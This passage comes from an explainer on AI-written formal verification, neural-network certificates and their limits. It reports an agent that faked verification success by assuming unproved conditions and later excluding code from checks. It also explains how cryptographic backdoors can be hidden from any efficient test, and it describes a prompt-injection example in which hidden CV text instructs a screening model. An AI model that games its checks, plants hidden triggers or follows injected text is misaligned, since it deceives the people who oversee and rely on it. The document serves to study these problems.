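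Philipp chose the overall direction, picked among options the agent proposed and reviewed the specifications, but wrote none of the agents' code, contracts or proofs. He also had to watch for cheating. While working on ML-KEM, the agent could not prove some conditions, so it told GNATprove to assume them and reported success. Philipp banned this, and the agent later began excluding code from verification instead. An automatic ban on exclusions would not work, because some code, such as the part that handles network connections, has to be excluded.

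Philipp estimates that supervising the agents took 20 to 40 times less work than verifying comparable code by hand. The estimate comes from one comparison, in which a junior developer needed about six weeks for FrodoKEM and Philipp spent about six hours supervising. This is reasonable evidence that the saving is large, but a single comparison can't reliably show how large.

### Benchmark results

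*A benchmark for vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, 2025), an early large benchmark, collected 12,504 specifications and asked models to write code and a proof for each. Models succeeded on 82% of the specifications in Dafny, 44% in Verus (a verifier for Rust programs) and 27% in Lean. The problems differed between languages, so the rates are only roughly comparable. One likely reason for the gap is that Dafny and Verus leave much of the reasoning to a solver, while in Lean the model has to construct more of the proof itself.

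*VeriContest* (Xie, Pawagi and colleagues, 2026) tests separately whether a model can write correct code and whether it can prove code correct. It contains 1,006 programming puzzles from the websites LeetCode and Codeforces, each with a specification, a Rust program, a Verus proof and tests. GPT-5.5 wrote correct code for 97.5% of the puzzles. When given the correct code and specification, it produced a valid proof on the first attempt for only 13.8%.

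Feedback from the verifier helped GPT-5.5 finish many more proofs. On a sample of 200 puzzles, ten independent attempts raised the share it finished to 20.5%, while ten rounds of repair using the verifier's error messages raised it to 48.5%.

By October 2026, proof was no longer the bottleneck on these puzzles. In *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier*, Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues (2026) translated the puzzles into Lean and let Claude Opus 5.5 submit each proof for checking up to 40 times. Opus proved all 1,325 theorems, covering every puzzle, at a median of 3.4 minutes and $1.20 per theorem. The cheaper Claude Sonnet 5.5 proved the 50 theorems that had taken Opus longest.

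Serbanuta and colleagues make the tool they tested, but this conflict of interest matters less than usual because Lean's proof checker accepted every proof. They also ran Opus 5.5 with Verus on the 50 puzzles with the longest published proofs, and it proved 49. The model may have remembered some of the Verus proofs, which had been public since May, but it could not have remembered Lean proofs of these theorems because none existed. The median VeriContest program has 33 lines, and it is still unknown how well this works on larger programs.

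Models have done less well at writing specifications. GPT-5.5 wrote a correct one for 57.2% of the VeriContest puzzles. *Verus-SpecGym* (Agarwal, Neamtu and colleagues, 2026) let agents use Verus and other tools while writing specifications for 581 Codeforces puzzles. The best model, Gemini 3.1 Pro, succeeded on 77.8% of them, and the other leading models succeeded on 51% to 58%.

| Task | Given to the model | Best result |
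|---|---|---|
| Verus proof, one attempt (Xie and colleagues) | Specification and code | 13.8% (GPT-5.5) |
| Verus proof, ten rounds of repair (Xie and colleagues) | Specification and code | 48.5% (GPT-5.5) |
| Lean proof, up to 40 checks (Serbanuta and colleagues) | Specification, code and description in words | 100% (Claude Opus 5.5) |
| Specification, one attempt (Xie and colleagues) | Description in words | 57.2% (GPT-5.5) |
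| Specification, agent with tools (Agarwal and colleagues) | Description in words | 77.8% (Gemini 3.1 Pro) |
| Specification, code and proof together, one attempt (Xie and colleagues) | Description in words | 6.8% (GPT-5.5) |

The scores for specifications come from models that OpenAI and Google have since replaced, so current models would probably score higher. But specifications are also inherently harder than proofs, because no checker can confirm that a specification matches what someone asked for in words. With a proof, an agent can use the checker's errors to revise its work until the checker accepts it.

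Some benchmarks now score the program, its theorems and their proofs together. Miranda, Daruru and colleagues built *VeriBench* (2026), a set of 884 tasks in which an agent turns a Python program into a Lean program with theorems and proofs. A failure at any stage sharply lowers the score. *VeriBench launch*, the project's announcement, describes a Lean file that a weaker score would reward. The file defines addition, passes two tests and states a theorem that the definition is correct. It compiles, but instead of a proof it has only "sorry", Lean's placeholder for a missing proof.

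### Valid proofs that establish little

A missing proof is easy to detect. It is harder to notice that a finished proof is about the wrong statement. Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026), in *Verified but Vacuous*, propose judging AI-written verified code with three tests:

1. Does the verifier accept the program?
2. Is the proof tied to the specification, meaning that the program's postcondition refers to the separate definition of what the task requires?
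3. Is that specification true to the requirement?

They applied the first two tests to an existing method, in which a model writes a program in Dafny and a tool converts it to Python. Claude Opus 4.7 wrote ten solutions to each of 164 short problems. Dafny accepted 99.1% of them, but only 1.9% of the accepted programs had a postcondition that referred to a named specification.

As Vempaty and colleagues point out, this gap alone does not show that the other proofs were empty. For example, a program that doubles x might have the postcondition that the result equals 2x. This postcondition describes the task completely but fails the second test because it doesn't refer to a separate definition. A named specification would pass that test even if it were always true.

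A better sign that the proofs were empty is that 94.7% of the accepted programs had no postcondition. Dafny had proved basic facts about those programs, such as that they finish, but nothing general about their results. The prompt probably caused this, because its example had no postcondition, only a list of expected results, which Dafny assumes are correct during verification and checks when the program runs.

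Most of the programs were still right, since 92.6% of all the solutions passed the benchmark's basic tests. But the evidence that they were right came from those tests, and a customer who heard that 99.1% of the programs were "verified" would probably have thought it came from the proofs.

Vempaty and colleagues use the task of finding the largest number in a list to show how a program can pass the first two tests and fail the third. In simplified form, it looks like this:

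```
specification MaxCorrect(nums, result):
    result ≥ 0

program Max(nums):
    postcondition: MaxCorrect(nums, result)
    result = 0
```

For the list [5, 3, 7], the program returns 0, although the correct answer is 7. The verifier still accepts the program because it only has to prove that 0 ≥ 0, which is true for every list. The specification is also too strict. The largest number in [−3, −1] is −1, but the verifier would reject a program that returned it because it is below zero.

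A faithful specification of a function that returns the largest number in a list requires that the result is in the list and that no number in the list is greater. Without the first requirement, 100 would be an acceptable answer for [5, 3, 7], and without the second, 3 would be. The specification also needs a precondition that the list is not empty, because an empty list has no largest number.

Vempaty and colleagues found the same problem in their own system, which rejects any program whose postcondition doesn't refer to the specification. Of the Rust programs it fully verified, 11.5% failed hidden tests on one benchmark and 14.8% on the LeetCode part of VeriContest. Some of these failures may come from the translation into Rust or from the tests themselves.

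On VeriContest, 1,316 solutions were verified and passed the tests, but only 535 of them (40.7%) also had a specification that passed Xie and colleagues' checks. In the other cases, the code worked, but the specification did not reliably describe what it should do. If a specification is too weak, the verifier may later accept an agent's edit that breaks the code.

### How specifications go wrong

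Agarwal and colleagues illustrate the main kinds of error with a simple search problem. A program must return the first position of a number k in a sorted list, counting from zero, or −1 if k is absent. For k = 20 in [10, 20, 20, 20, 30], the answer is 1.

- A specification that requires each number to be greater than the one before excludes this list, which is a valid input.
- One that forgets to require a sorted list admits inputs that the program was never meant to handle.
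- One that requires a position in the list rejects −1, the right answer when k is absent.
- One that accepts any position where 20 occurs would allow 3.

The first error can be the most dangerous for security because an attacker can still send the inputs that the precondition excludes, and the proof doesn't cover them. The second and third errors are usually easy to notice because they make a correct program fail to verify.

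In *VerusEval*, Wang, Jiang and colleagues (2026) measured how common such errors are. They collected 13,716 Rust programs for which models had written both the contract and the proof. Of those that Verus accepted, only 42.3% passed three further checks: the contract was not trivial, it gave the right verdict on sample inputs and outputs, and Verus could prove it equivalent to a reference contract. In one failure, the task was to return the shortest list in a collection. The contract required the result to be as short as the shortest list but didn't require it to come from the collection, so a program given [1, 2] and [3] could return [9].

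The 42.3% figure probably underestimates how many contracts were correct. Verus may fail to prove that two equivalent contracts are equivalent, and the reference itself may be wrong. Wang and colleagues flagged 61 suspicious references and judged 36 probably defective. After they repaired one reference, 10 of the 11 contracts that had failed against it were equivalent to the repaired version.

People also write faulty specifications, as the Wi-Fi proof that missed KRACK showed. *CLEVER* (Thakur, Lee and colleagues, 2025) contains 161 problems in which a model has to write a specification that matches a hidden, human-written reference, then write a Lean program and prove it correct. In *Isomorphism Is Not Enough*, Sosso, Arora and Spitters (2026) had three AI agents attempt every problem and explain any failure, and concluded that 80 of the 161 references were arguably wrong. Thakur, Lee and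 colleagues reviewed and accepted all 80 findings.

By CLEVER's own scoring, the agents completed up to 59 of the 161 problems, compared with one in the original study. The best agent wrote an arguably valid specification for 98.8% of the 161 problems. This rate is much higher than in other studies, partly because the agents judged validity themselves, although Sosso and colleagues inspected the best agent's work. Comparing AI-written specifications with human ones therefore measures errors in both.

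For 13 problems, the description in words had more than one reasonable reading. The request for the file reader is also ambiguous, because it doesn't specify how to handle a very large genuine file. An agent can prove its program correct under either reading, but only the person who made the request knows which one is right.

Existing code can also mislead a model. *Are LLM-Generated Formal Specifications Faithful to Their Requirements?* (2026) tested models on incorrect programs and found that only about a quarter received a well-formed specification that matched the requirement. The specifications that accepted the faulty code more often copied its mistake than left something out. For the original file reader, such a specification might define `size` as 8 × n after wrapping, which the flawed code satisfies. This is a good reason to write the contract before the code, as Philipp's agents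 did.

#### Formal descriptions that do not match the code

The test in which Claude gave the textbook version of an algorithm instead of describing Etcd came from a benchmark called SysMoBench. The benchmark's team explains in a SIGOPS article, *Can LLMs model real-world systems in TLA+?*, that it records steps from real runs of a system and checks whether the model's formal description allows each step.

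In one case, Claude Sonnet incorrectly described how ZooKeeper, a program that coordinates groups of servers, elects a leader. In the real code, a server's new vote replaces its old one. Claude's description kept both, so it could count votes that had been replaced.

The models averaged about 46% for agreement with the real code when they wrote a description without exploring the code themselves. The same team's agent, Specula, reads the code and decides what to describe, and it gets full marks on the current tasks. This suggests that much of the problem was how the researchers used the models, although the team designed both the agent and the test.

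#### An impossible assumption

A model can also make a false statement provable by changing the statement's assumptions. In *FaithformBench*, Cornish, Ghinassi and colleagues (2026) inserted errors into steps from mathematical arguments and asked models to translate the steps into Lean. One faulty step said that if 3ˣ = 5, then 3ˣ⁺² = 51. The right value is 45, because 3ˣ⁺² is 9 × 3ˣ. A small model called Kimina translated the step but declared x to be a natural number. No natural number satisfies 3ˣ = 5, so the assumption is never true and anything follows from it, including 3ˣ⁺² = 51.

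Cornish and colleagues found many such silent corrections in all four models trained for this kind of translation. The one that translated correct steps best was also the most likely, on the harder problems, to make wrong steps provable. General-purpose models, including Claude Opus 4.7, did this much less. The study is about mathematics, but an impossible precondition has the same effect on a program's contract.

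### Ways to check a specification

A verifier can easily catch some of these errors by testing whether a precondition is impossible or a postcondition is always true. These tests would expose an assumption like 3ˣ = 5, but they would miss `MaxCorrect` because "result ≥ 0" is false for negative results.

#### Running the postcondition

Xie and colleagues wrote Post2Exe, a tool that turns a postcondition into an ordinary program they can run on outputs known to be right or wrong. For [5, 3, 7], `MaxCorrect` should accept 7 and reject 0, 3 and 100, but it accepts all four, so it fails the check.

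This found 60 incomplete postconditions in VeriContest's own specifications, which experts were supposed to have reviewed. For example, the specification for a puzzle that asks for the first and last positions of a number in a list accepted −9 and −8.

The check covers only the cases that somebody tries, and it needs a reliable source of correct answers. In Wang and colleagues' study, only 63.2% of the contracts that passed such tests were provably equivalent to the reference. Agarwal and colleagues added to their tests inputs that Codeforces competitors had designed to break each other's programs, and these exposed faulty specifications that the official tests had missed. Post2Exe also couldn't convert about 15% of the postconditions, such as those about infinitely many values.

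#### Mutating the code

Planting a bug also tests the specification. If an engineer replaced a correct search for the maximum with `result = 0`, the verifier would still accept the program, which would show that `MaxCorrect` is too weak. Xie and colleagues used mutated programs in a related way, to generate plausible wrong outputs for testing postconditions.

Some mutations don't change what a program does, so a person has to review the ones that survive. Mutation also can't expose a requirement that is missing from both the code and the specification. For example, if a server never checks who owns a file, there is no ownership check to remove to test whether the specification requires one.

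#### Mechanical translation

A mechanical translator makes it much more likely that a proof applies to the actual program. *AutoSpec* (2026) and Serbanuta and colleagues translate Rust into Lean with tools based on Aeneas. Rust lets only one part of a program change a value at a time, so Aeneas can turn a function that changes a value in place into one that takes the old value and returns a new one.

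Serbanuta and colleagues ran 105 of the translated programs on 19,555 test cases, and every result matched the Rust original. However, they had to rewrite some of the code or specification for 27 puzzles because their tools could not handle features such as hash maps. Tolmach and Klaus note that fixing a translator's rule fixes every program that uses it, whereas an AI model may make a different mistake each time. But a faithful translation preserves flaws in the code and its specification, so `Max` would still return 0 and `MaxCorrect` would still accept it.

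#### Human review

Reviewers can in principle ignore the proof and read only the specification. This saves the most work when the specification is much shorter than the code. In VeriContest, the median specification has 26 lines and the median program has 33, so a reviewer who reads only the specification reads almost as much as one who reads the program. The saving may be larger for software with a complicated implementation and a simple purpose, such as a fast sorting routine.

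Reviewers also miss errors, as the audit of CLEVER and the 60 weak postconditions in VeriContest show. Another AI model can help, but in Agarwal and colleagues' study, a model acting as judge missed 26% of the failures that running the specifications had caught. Human review is the only one of these checks that can catch a requirement missing from the code, the specification and the tests, and only if the reviewer thinks of it.

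### Will verification become mainstream?

Kleppmann predicted in 2025 that AI would bring formal verification into the mainstream, because models make proofs cheap, a proof checker rejects any mistakes they make, and people would rather have a proof of AI-written code than review all of it by hand. The VeriContest results strongly support the claim about cost, at least for small programs, where a proof that might have taken an expert hours now costs about a dollar.

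Kleppmann also expected writing specifications to become the difficult part, and thought that AI could help with that too, with a manageable risk of losing subtleties in translation. The evidence on that risk is less favourable, because models often write specifications that are wrong in ways the verifier cannot detect, and tests and reviewers catch only some of the errors. Models' scores are improving, and many of the human-written reference specifications were wrong too, so the risk may prove manageable where people test specifications as carefully as they test code. Many evaluations report only how many programs a verifier accepted, which hides these errors.

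Verification is therefore likely to spread first where an exact definition already exists. Philipp suggests that standards bodies publish their standards in machine-checkable form. The swapped values in the SSH code would then have caused a proof to fail. Most business software has no standard to publish, and the people who run the business may never have written down their rules about who can see which records.

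## Can a neural network itself be verified?

A neural network runs as an ordinary program. It multiplies its inputs by stored numbers called weights, adds up the results, applies a simple function and repeats this for each layer. An engineer could prove that this program is memory-safe, as with the file reader. But that proof would hold for any weights, so it would not show whether the network can tell a stop sign from a speed limit sign. A proof about the network's decisions has to account for the weights, which come from training, so no programmer can explain why a particular weight has its value.

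### Robustness certificates

Changes to an image that are too small for a person to notice can make a network label it differently. Verification researchers have therefore concentrated on one property. A robustness certificate is a proof that a network's decision stays the same for every input within a stated distance of a given one. If the network puts input x in class c, and ε is the distance, the theorem is:

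```
for every x′ such that |x′ᵢ − xᵢ| ≤ ε for every i:
    score(c, x′) > score(d, x′) for every other class d
```

For an image, each xᵢ is the brightness of one pixel in one colour, usually on a scale with 255 steps. With ε = 2/255, all of these values may change at the same time, each by up to two steps.

This specification is easy to write because it uses the network's own answer at x as the standard, so nobody has to define what a stop sign looks like. A network that mislabels the original image can therefore have a valid certificate for the wrong label.

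### A network small enough to check by hand

This network has two inputs and two neurons. ReLU(z) is z if z is positive and 0 otherwise. The network's decision is "yes" if y is positive.

```
h1 = ReLU(x1 + x2)
h2 = ReLU(x1 − x2)
y  = h1 − h2
```

At the point (1, 0.6), h1 is 1.6 and h2 is 0.4, so y is 1.2 and the decision is "yes". The simplest way to look for a certificate is to compute an interval for each quantity, as abstract interpretation does for ordinary programs.

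| | Each input may move by 0.2 | Each input may move by 0.4 |
|---|---|---|
| x1 + x2 | 1.2 to 2.0 | 0.8 to 2.4 |
| x1 − x2 | 0 to 0.8 | −0.4 to 1.2 |
| h1 | 1.2 to 2.0 | 0.8 to 2.4 |
| h2 | 0 to 0.8 | 0 to 1.2 |
| y = h1 − h2 | 0.4 to 2.0 | −0.4 to 2.4 |

The first column is a certificate because y is at least 0.4. The second proves nothing, even though y can't reach its lower bound of −0.4. That would require h1 to be 0.8, which needs x1 at its lowest value, and h2 to be 1.2, which needs x1 at its highest. The intervals don't capture that h1 and h2 both depend on x1, just as they didn't capture the connection between `size` and i in the file reader.

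Splitting the problem into two cases recovers it. If x1 is at least x2, then y = (x1 + x2) − (x1 − x2) = 2 × x2, which is at least 0.4 because x2 is at least 0.2. If x1 is less than x2, then h2 is 0 and y = x1 + x2. Both inputs are then at least 0.6, so y is at least 1.2. The true minimum is therefore 0.4, and the decision is "yes" throughout the larger region too.

### Bound propagation and branch and bound

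Carrying bounds through a network from layer to layer is called bound propagation. Most current verifiers carry more than intervals. One common method encloses each ReLU between straight lines, which keep track of the inputs. When x1 − x2 lies between −0.4 and 1.2, h2 is never above the line 0.75 × (x1 − x2) + 0.3. Since h1 is simply x1 + x2 here, this gives:

```
y ≥ (x1 + x2) − 0.75 × (x1 − x2) − 0.3
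  = 0.25 × x1 + 1.75 × x2 − 0.3
  ≥ 0.2
```

This proves that the decision is stable without any splitting, although the bound is still below the true minimum. If each input may move by 0.5, the same method gives a bound of only −0.1, while the true minimum is 0.2. The textbook *Introduction to Neural Network Verification* (2021) covers other shapes, such as zonotopes and polyhedra, which can fit the possible values more closely but take more computation.

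When the bounds are inconclusive, a verifier can use branch and bound. It picks a ReLU whose input could be on either side of zero, splits the problem at zero and computes new bounds for each half. It keeps splitting inconclusive pieces until it has proved every piece or found a counterexample. In the small network, a movement of 0.7 allows the point (1, −0.1), where y is −0.2.

Each undecided neuron can double the number of pieces, much as each branch in a program can double the number of paths. With 300 undecided neurons, there could be about 2 × 10⁹⁰ pieces.

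In 2017 Guy Katz and colleagues published Reluplex, an early solver for ReLU networks, and proved that the exact problem is NP-complete. A fast method that worked for every network would therefore also quickly solve a famously hard kind of puzzle, in which true-or-false variables must satisfy a long list of clauses. With 1 for true and 0 for false, the clause "a or b or not c", for example, can be written as the neuron ReLU(c − a − b), which outputs 1 if the clause fails and 0 if it holds. For each variable x between 0 and 1, the term x − ReLU(2x − 1) is zero only if x is exactly 0 or 1. The puzzle has a solution exactly when some input makes the sum of all the neuron outputs and variable terms zero, so a verifier that can always tell whether this sum stays above zero can solve the puzzle.

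This result concerns the worst case, and many networks are easier to verify. Katz and colleagues tested Reluplex on ACAS Xu, a set of 45 small networks that advise aircraft how to turn to avoid a collision. One of its ten properties is that the network must not advise "clear of conflict" when another aircraft is straight ahead and approaching. Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026) write in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)* that the original checks took from seconds to days, and some never finished. In the 2026 competition, three tools settled all 186 ACAS Xu cases with a limit of 116 seconds each. Four tools also solved all 100 networks that the organisers had built from logic puzzles, though the puzzles were small, with at most 100 variables.

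### What verifiers can handle in 2026

The competition ran 13 tools on the same set of problems. The winner, α,β-CROWN, combines bound propagation on graphics processors with branch and bound. It found either a proof or a counterexample in 3,164 of the 3,373 cases in the main track, or 94%. This rate varied widely between kinds of network.

| Networks | Largest number of weights | Cases | Proofs by α,β-CROWN | Counterexamples |
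|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sentence classifiers | 4,000 | 1,080 | 418 | 662 |
| ACAS Xu | 13,000 | 186 | 139 | 47 |
| Small vision transformers | 76,000 | 200 | 123 | 0 |
| Malware classifiers | 1.5 million | 150 | 121 | 29 |
| Image classifier with 200 classes | 3.6 million | 200 | 139 | 38 |
| VGG16 image classifier | 138 million | 18 | 18 | 0 |

VGG16 is the largest network in the competition. Its 18 properties range from changes to a single pixel to changes to all 150,528 input values, so some are much weaker than others.

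The vision transformers have less than a thousandth as many weights as VGG16, yet α,β-CROWN could not decide 77 of their 200 cases, even though each pixel value could change by only one brightness step. These networks use the same basic design as language models, but the benchmark's creators had shrunk them to two or three layers and replaced one operation with a simpler one. Another tool, ACT, reported proofs for all 200 cases. That result needs confirmation because the creators had removed most images with known counterexamples, so a false proof would probably have gone unnoticed.

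Transformers are hard to verify partly because their attention layers multiply quantities that both depend on the input. Suppose x can be anything from 0 to 1. Interval arithmetic bounds x × x between 0 and 1, and therefore x − x × x between −1 and 1, although the true range is 0 to 0.25. *Parameterized Abstract Interpretation for Transformer Verification* (2026) derives tighter bounds for such products, and its method proves many cases that earlier methods could not.

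Memory also limits verification, because standard tools have to fit a network's weights and the coefficients of its bounds on one graphics processor. In *Scaling Neural Network Verification with Tensor Parallelism and Fully Sharded Data Parallelism*, Vorobyov and Ilyushin (2026) spread the work over several processors, using methods adapted from the training of large models. This allows larger networks but doesn't tighten loose bounds.

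Engineers can also train networks to be easier to certify, but this makes them less accurate. Ladner and colleagues give results for CIFAR-10, a standard set of small images. Ordinary networks label well over 95% of these images correctly. One network trained for certification labelled 83.5% of the test images correctly, and α,β-CROWN could certify 66.0% as both correct and stable at ε = 2/255. For a similar network at ε = 8/255, these figures were 57.2% and 35.5%.

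The results also depend on trusting the verifiers. Eight of the 13 tools gave at least one wrong answer or a counterexample that failed the organisers' check. The winner did so once, on a benchmark with deliberately hidden counterexamples. The organisers aim in the long term to require proofs that another program can check, as a proof assistant does. Until then, anyone relying on a result has to trust the whole verifier. The runner-up, Vibecheck, settled 3,108 cases. Claude Code wrote almost all of the tool over two months, which makes independent checking even more useful.

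Even a correct certificate may cover very little. One benchmark considers only movements of about a hundredth of a millimetre in a robot's camera. The problem is more serious for the malware classifiers, because an attacker disguising a program can rewrite as much of it as they like and has no reason to stay within the certified bound ε.

### Randomized smoothing

Randomized smoothing gives a certificate without analyzing the network's internals, so it works for much larger networks. It adds random noise to the input many times, runs the network on each noisy copy and returns the most common answer. Jeremy Cohen, Elan Rosenfeld and Zico Kolter proved its main theorem in 2019.

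Suppose the noise follows a normal distribution with standard deviation σ, and a share p of all possible noisy copies, more than half, would receive the same answer. The most common answer then cannot change until the input has moved by at least:

```
R = σ × Φ⁻¹(p)
```

Here Φ⁻¹ is the inverse of the normal distribution function. If p is 97.7%, for example, R is twice σ. The formula works because a small change to the input barely changes the distribution of noisy copies, so the share of copies receiving each answer can change only gradually.

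The formula is exact, but p has to be estimated because nobody can run the network on every noisy copy. Cohen and colleagues used 100,000 copies of each image and accepted a 0.1% chance that a certificate was wrong. The guarantee is therefore statistical, unlike a proof by branch and bound. It also applies only to the vote over noisy copies, not to a single run of the original network.

Cohen and colleagues certified their classifier's predictions as correct and stable for R = 0.5 on 49% of the test images from ImageNet, a large photo collection. R limits the total straight-line distance between the original and altered images, not the change to each pixel. An attacker who spread the change evenly over an image's 150,528 values could move each by only about a third of a brightness step.

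In *What, Indeed, is an Achievable Provable Guarantee for Learning-Enabled Safety Critical Systems*, Bensalem, Cheng and colleagues (2023) argue for a different kind of statistical guarantee, one that limits the chance that a network fails on the next input, weighting inputs by how often they occur in use. This makes sense for a car in ordinary traffic, but like the statistics from fuzzing, it offers little protection against an attacker who chooses the inputs.

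### Why a certificate can fail on a real machine

Most verifiers treat a network's arithmetic as exact, but the computers that run networks round their results. In 32-bit floating-point arithmetic, 100,000,000 + 1 − 100,000,000 gives 0 when computed from left to right, because representable numbers in that range are eight apart. Subtracting first gives 1. Processors and software libraries add long sums in different orders, so the same network can give slightly different scores on two machines.

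In 2021 Kai Jia and Martin Rinard exploited this gap. They found images whose labels a verifier could only barely prove stable, then altered them within the certified distance so that the running network labelled them differently. The same year, Dániel Zombori and colleagues built a network with a hidden second behaviour that a supposedly exact verifier missed because of rounding. Tiny random changes to the weights defeated this particular trick.

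Attila Szász, Balázs Bánhelyi and Márk Jelasity extended the attack in 2025 by designing networks that detect the order or precision of the arithmetic, much as the sum above does, and change their behaviour accordingly. Some verifiers allow for rounding in their own calculations, but this doesn't account for how another machine will round. Every verifier the researchers tested approved networks that misbehaved once deployed.

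The competition's organisers faced a milder version of the problem. Their earlier rules allowed a small tolerance, so one tool could prove a property while another found a "counterexample" slightly outside the permitted inputs, and both could count as correct. In 2026 they required inputs to meet the specification exactly and checked every counterexample with one fixed version of the software. Ladner and colleagues acknowledge that borderline cases could still give different results elsewhere.

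The danger from rounding depends on who made the network. A company that trained its own can ask for a proof with some margin, such as y > 0.01 instead of y > 0, and ordinary rounding will rarely matter. If a supplier designed the network to exploit rounding, a margin is not enough, and the proof has to model the arithmetic of the machine that will run the network.

### What could anyone specify for a language model?

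Sanjit Seshia, Dorsa Sadigh and Shankar Sastry point out that formal verification needs a model of the system, a model of its environment and a property to check. In one of their examples, a car brakes automatically when a neural network recognises an obstacle in the camera image. Because nobody can write a formula for what a pedestrian looks like, they suggest starting with a property of the whole car, that it keeps a minimum distance from any object, and then working out what the network must get right for the car to do so.

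The environment is also difficult to model. If the model of traffic lets other drivers do anything, a crash is always possible and the safety property is false. If the model rules out too much behavior, the proof misses real dangers.

A chatbot's environment is whoever writes the prompt. GPT-2, a small language model from 2019, has a vocabulary of about 50,000 tokens, so there are about 10⁹⁴ possible 20-token prompts.

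There is no formula for the property "writes no harmful text", because whether text is harmful depends on context. The same instructions for growing a bacterium may be routine in a hospital laboratory and dangerous elsewhere. An engineer could instead specify that a second network never rates the output as harmful, which can be written as a formula. But the specification would then include every mistake the second network makes, and a proof would show only that the output passes that network's check. A list of harmful examples is precise but covers only what is on the list.

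*On the Verification of ML Systems and Models*, by Dolcetti, Arceri and colleagues, suggests adapting robustness to generated text by requiring similar prompts to give similar outputs. Somebody would still have to define "similar". Adding a single word such as "not" may call for a completely different answer, and two prompts with no words in common may call for the same one.

Some useful requirements can be stated exactly. Suppose a company puts a password in the model's instructions. "No prompt makes the model print the password" is easy to write as a formula, but a model could satisfy it and still print the password backwards. Noninterference rules out such leaks by requiring that, for every prompt, the output has the same probabilities whatever the password is. Although this specification is clear, no verifier can prove that a model of useful size meets it, and the model may not. Protections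 outside the model can enforce some such rules, for example by never giving it the password.

### What researchers have proved about language models

The competition's sentence classifiers come closest to an everyday use. One detects when a user asks whether they are talking to a robot, and the other concerns medical questions. The benchmark's creators generated paraphrases of each sentence, used a language model to turn each paraphrase into a list of 30 numbers, and drew the smallest box that contained them all. The verifier then had to show that a small classifier gave the right answer everywhere in the box.

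α,β-CROWN proved this for 418 boxes and found counterexamples in the other 662. Neither result translates directly into a statement about sentences. A counterexample may be a list of numbers that no sentence produces, and a paraphrase that nobody generated may fall outside the box. The proofs also leave out the language model that produced the numbers.

Other proofs cover parts of a language model. *Towards Verifiable Transformers* (2026) verifies a mechanism that closes quotation marks in a model the size of GPT-2. The researchers first removed one of the model's standard operations and replaced some of its attention heads with short programs. Their result covers 1,280 listed prompts. Running all of them would be enough to check the model's output, so the proof is more interesting for what it establishes about the internal mechanism.

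In *The Misery of Mechanistic Interpretability*, Ladner and Althoff (2026) verify tools for interpreting models. A language model's neurons are hard to interpret because each responds to many unrelated things, so researchers train a stand-in network that imitates one layer using features people can label, such as "pathogen". A safety auditor might read those labels to decide whether to block a request, so it matters whether the stand-in still matches the real layer when someone rewords the request.

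To test this, Ladner and Althoff considered replacing words in sentences with synonyms and enclosed the resulting activity at each layer of GPT-2 in a continuous region. A verifier then proved an upper limit on how much the stand-in could differ from the real layer anywhere in that region. The gap was substantial at every layer and generally grew in later ones. Retraining one stand-in with verification in mind cut the proven limit by about 90%, but only two or three of its 20 most active features provably stayed in the top 20.

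These results cover one layer at a time. Combining them would require each layer's region to contain every output the previous layer could produce. The current regions are too small, by a factor of about five in one case, and the verifiers cannot yet handle the whole model.

A better verifier would not always produce a certificate, because the property is often false. Replacing a single word with a synonym changed GPT-2's prediction of the next token in 21% of Ladner and Althoff's tests. In those cases, a verifier could at most find a counterexample.

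*Evaluating and Improving the Robustness of Large Language Models* (2026) states that most defences for language models, including training on human feedback, still lack provable guarantees. It predicts that verifying individual properties of models with billions of weights will become feasible. Progress on image networks makes that plausible for robustness to small input changes, but proving that a model avoids harm would also require a definition of harm, which that work does not provide.

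### Backdoors that no efficient test can find

A network from an untrusted supplier may contain a backdoor, a hidden trigger that makes it give whatever answer the supplier wants. In 2022 Shafi Goldwasser, Michael Kim, Vinod Vaikuntanathan and Or Zamir showed that, under standard cryptographic assumptions, a supplier can hide a backdoor from every efficient test.

The first method uses a digital signature, which only the holder of a secret key can create but anyone can check. The network interprets small details of the input as a message with a signature. If the signature is valid, the network gives the answer the supplier chose. Otherwise it behaves normally. A tester who can only run the network would have to forge a signature to trigger the backdoor, but one who can examine the weights might notice the part that checks signatures.

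The second method also hides the backdoor from people who have the weights and the training data, but it works only for certain simple networks. Training these networks starts from random numbers, which the supplier draws from a slightly altered distribution. Telling the altered distribution from the proper one would require solving a problem that cryptographers believe is hard.

This second result limits what robustness certificates can do. A fast, sound verifier could never certify the backdoored version of such a network, because a small change to the input can trigger the backdoor, so the network isn't robust. If the verifier could usually certify the clean version, its results would reveal the backdoor, which the cryptographic assumption rules out. It must therefore nearly always fail to certify the clean version too. A valid certificate would still guarantee robustness, but buyers could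 hardly ever get one.

The argument applies to specific constructions. It doesn't show that every network is impossible to certify, and it doesn't rule out slow verifiers. In 2024 Andis Draguns and colleagues brought the threat closer to language models by building cryptographic circuits into the weights of transformers. A defender with full access to those weights still could not produce the trigger, though they might notice that the weights looked unusual.

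Also in 2024, Goldwasser and other colleagues showed that a defender can sometimes remove a backdoor without detecting it. In the simplest case, the defender knows that the correct answer is a linear function f of the input, so f(x) = f(x + r) − f(r) for any r. The defender picks r at random, runs the network on x + r and on r, and subtracts the second answer from the first. Both inputs look random, so a trigger hidden in x no longer works. If the network is right on nearly all random inputs, the result is very probably correct.

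This defence requires knowing the mathematical form of the correct answer in advance. Goldwasser and colleagues extended it to polynomials and some other functions, but nobody knows such a form for the right reply to a prompt.

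## What can be guaranteed about a system whose model cannot be verified?

Engineers who can't prove anything useful about a language model may still be able to prove something about the ordinary code around it. On the HACMS helicopter, the seL4 kernel confined unverified camera software. Researchers now design AI agents in a similar way. They assume the model may produce any output, and they write checkable code that limits what the output can do.

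### Prompt injection

The main reason to assume the worst about an unverified model is prompt injection, in which someone places text in data that a language model reads, and the model follows it as an instruction. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* gives the example of a job applicant whose CV contains hidden text telling the recruiter's model to approve it for interview.

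David C, who works at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, contrasts prompt injection with SQL injection, in which an attacker types database commands into a web form. Programmers can prevent SQL injection by sending the command and the data separately, so that the database never treats data as a command. A language model can't separate them this way, because it receives instructions and data as one sequence of tokens and predicts the next token. He therefore thinks prompt injection may never have a complete fix.

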